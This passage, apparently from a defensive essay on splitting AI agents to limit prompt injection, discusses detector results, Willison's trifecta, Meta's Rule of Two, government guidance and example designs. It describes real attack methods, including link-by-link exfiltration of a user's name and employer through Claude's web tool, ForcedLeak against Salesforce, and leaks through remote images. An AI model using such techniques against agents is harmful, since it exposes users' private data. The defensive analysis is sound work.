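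At least one malicious hint got past the detector in 57 of the 232 tasks. The Safe Agent carried out the attack in 11 of those 57 (about one in five), or 4.7% of all tasks. Much of the protection therefore came from the detector rather than the length limit.

Hu and colleagues attribute the 11 successful attacks to chance, because none succeeded again when they reran each of those tasks five times. If attacks had a 4.7% chance of success, all 55 reruns would fail about 7% of the time, so the reruns don't rule out that explanation. But a project that accepts bug reports from anyone would still be at risk, because if each report independently had a 4.7% chance of working, an attacker who filed 15 would probably succeed at least once. Hu and colleagues didn't test an attack that adapted over several turns, because it would have cost too much.

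If attackers found reliable short injections, Twin Agent would keep running normally, but its length limit would no longer provide much protection. Attackers might find them through a longer search, or because a new model in the Safe Agent's role follows injected instructions more readily than the old one. The designer could shorten the hints, but more tasks would fail. Shortening them far enough would bring the design back to fixed choices and numbers, and with that restriction Jacob and colleagues' bug-fixing agent succeeded about a third less often.

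A designer who uses free-text hints should therefore repeat the attacks whenever the model changes, and limit the damage a bad hint can do. For example, a programming agent could work on a copy of the project, and a person could review the finished fix before it goes live. The person would then approve once per bug instead of once per command.

The bug-fixing test also treated the project's code as trusted, and the Safe Agent read it directly. In a project that includes outside packages, an injection in the code could reach the Safe Agent without passing through a hint.

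### Two rules for deciding when to split

Willison (2025) argues in *The lethal trifecta for AI agents* that no agent should combine private data, untrusted content and a way to send data out. A designer can apply this test without measuring anything. Willison usually prefers to remove the way to send data out, because this reduces the agent's usefulness least. OpenAI took this approach in June 2026 with Lockdown Mode, an optional ChatGPT setting that limits outbound network requests. An injection can still distort ChatGPT's answers in this mode. OpenAI's head of security described the mode as a tool for people at elevated risk, who may find the loss of features worthwhile.

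However, finding every route by which data can leave a system is hard. Anthropic restricted Claude's web-reading tool to addresses that the user had typed or a search had returned, but for a time the tool could also follow links on pages it had already read. The researcher Ayush Paul built a site with a link for each letter of the alphabet and got Claude to spell out the user's name, home city and employer to the site by following the links one by one. Anthropic has since stopped the tool from following such links.

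The trifecta also covers only data theft. In *New prompt injection papers* (2025), Willison calls this its one problem, because an injection can do other and worse damage. For example, it could make an agent with no access to private data delete a public website.

Meta's *Agents Rule of Two* (2025) tries to cover these cases. Within one session, an agent should have at most two of these properties:

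- A: it can process untrustworthy input.
- B: it has access to sensitive systems or private data.
- C: it can change something or communicate externally.

An agent that needs all three properties must be supervised, for example through human approval. Meta's example is a travel assistant that reads the web and knows the user's private details. It has to ask before every booking and can't visit web addresses it has composed itself. Meta also allows an agent to change its properties partway through a session. For instance, it could browse the web, then permanently lose the ability to communicate before opening internal files.

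Willison liked the rule at first but later objected that Meta's diagram marks the combination of A and C as safe, even though untrusted input can cause harmful changes when the agent has no private data. Meta could reply that any system worth protecting from such changes counts as sensitive, which would give the agent all three properties. Designers would then have to decide what is sensitive, which would make the rule harder to apply.

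The limit to one session is also a weakness if the agent has a memory, because an injection saved in one session can take effect in a later one. Human approval is a poor safeguard if people approve most of the dangerous requests. Meta warns that users may confirm without checking, and that involving a person is impractical in some background tasks.

Neither rule can show whether a particular split is good enough, because both treat exposure as either present or absent. OpenClaw's actor never opens emails, but it reads summaries of them, so by a strict count it still has all three elements of the trifecta. The rules are best for identifying a single agent that combines too many risky capabilities. After a split, the designer still has to examine what passes between the two halves.

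### Advice from industry and governments

The Frontier Model Forum's brief of June 2026 distinguishes agents that work inside an organisation, which could become insider threats, from agents that deal with the public, which receive more untrusted input. It doesn't give separate recommendations for each, but for agents in general it recommends narrow access, limits enforced by code outside the model, detectors to supplement those limits, and human confirmation for high-stakes or irreversible actions. It suggests that a ban on combining all three parts of the trifecta may suit higher-risk uses.

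The line between internal and public-facing agents can be unclear. In the ForcedLeak attack on Salesforce, an employee used an internal agent that read text submitted through a public web form. Designers should therefore classify an agent by who can write the text it reads rather than by who uses it.

The Forum also discusses granting permissions for a single task and revoking them immediately afterwards, but treats this as an open research question. Single-task permissions work badly for recurring jobs, such as updating a calendar from the inbox every day, and these jobs are among the main reasons people want agents.

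Government advice is stricter. On 1 May 2026, CISA (2026), the US cybersecurity agency, announced joint guidance with the National Security Agency and agencies from Australia, Canada, New Zealand and the United Kingdom. The guidance, *Careful adoption of agentic AI services*, recommends that organisations use agents only for low-risk, non-sensitive tasks and never give them broad or unrestricted access, especially to sensitive data or critical systems. Taken literally, this would rule out an assistant for a confidential mailbox, however well its designer separated its roles.

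The Australian Signals Directorate (2026) also advises organisations to deploy agents incrementally, which is more compatible with such products. An email assistant could start by only sorting messages, and a purchasing agent by only collecting quotes.

### Choosing a design for three systems

The two rules give different amounts of guidance for these systems:

| | Public help desk | Email assistant | Purchasing agent |
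|---|---|---|---|
| Text from outsiders | Customers' questions | Incoming mail | Suppliers' messages |
| Private data or sensitive systems | None | Mailbox, calendar | Purchase needs, price limits, payments |
| Ways to act | Replies to the person asking | Sends mail, changes the calendar | Asks for quotes, orders parts |
| Choice | No split | Two-part split | Full broker |

A help desk agent that answers questions from published manuals has nothing secret to reveal if it is hijacked. Adding a second agent would add cost and delay without protecting anything. The designer should instead give the single agent a fresh session for each customer and no tools beyond searching the manuals and replying.

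The remaining risk is a false or embarrassing answer. The delivery company DPD switched off its customer service bot in January 2024 after customers got it to use foul language, according to an Economist article that Willison quotes. Promising a refund could cost the company more. The design has to change if the help desk gains access to orders. Code could then retrieve only the logged-in customer's records, so the model never receives anyone else's. If the agent passes questions on to staff, any agents the staff use must treat that text as untrusted.

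The email assistant has all three parts of the trifecta, and its owner wants to keep them. A two-part split fits because much of the work is sorting, summarising and scheduling, and categories, dates and names can give the trusted agent most of what it needs for those tasks. The exposed agent reads the mail and returns these fields, and the trusted agent plans from them. Ordinary code lets the trusted agent send mail only to people in the owner's address book. Mail to anyone else needs the owner's approval, and these requests should be rare enough that the owner reads each one.

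A full broker would add less protection for letters than it does for purchases. It can check a letter's recipient against a list, but no fixed rule can decide whether a sentence belongs in the letter. The broker becomes worthwhile once the assistant can also pay for hotel rooms.

An attacker can still mislead the email assistant with a false date or a forged request. A reply drafted from private notes can also reveal too much to a permitted recipient, especially if someone has taken over a contact's account. The code should remove remote images even from mail the assistant sends to its owner. Microsoft's Copilot Cowork could send messages to its own user without approval, and opening one could leak data through the remote images in it.

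A two-part split isn't enough for the purchasing agent, because the agent that talks to suppliers could still commit the company's money. OpenAI's *Agent security in the enterprise* (2026) points out that a valid credential may give access to a system without establishing which actions are authorised. The pump manufacturer's broker can check whether an action is authorised against records the company already keeps, so its policy takes less work to write than one for a whole mailbox.

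Unusual orders will fail the broker's checks, and a person will have to handle them. The broker should send people only these orders, because they deserve more attention than routine ones. Suppliers can still persuade the purchasing agent to accept a poor deal within the limits. An error in the price list or a compromise of the broker could cost far more than one bad order, but a separate spending cap at the bank would limit that loss even if the broker failed.
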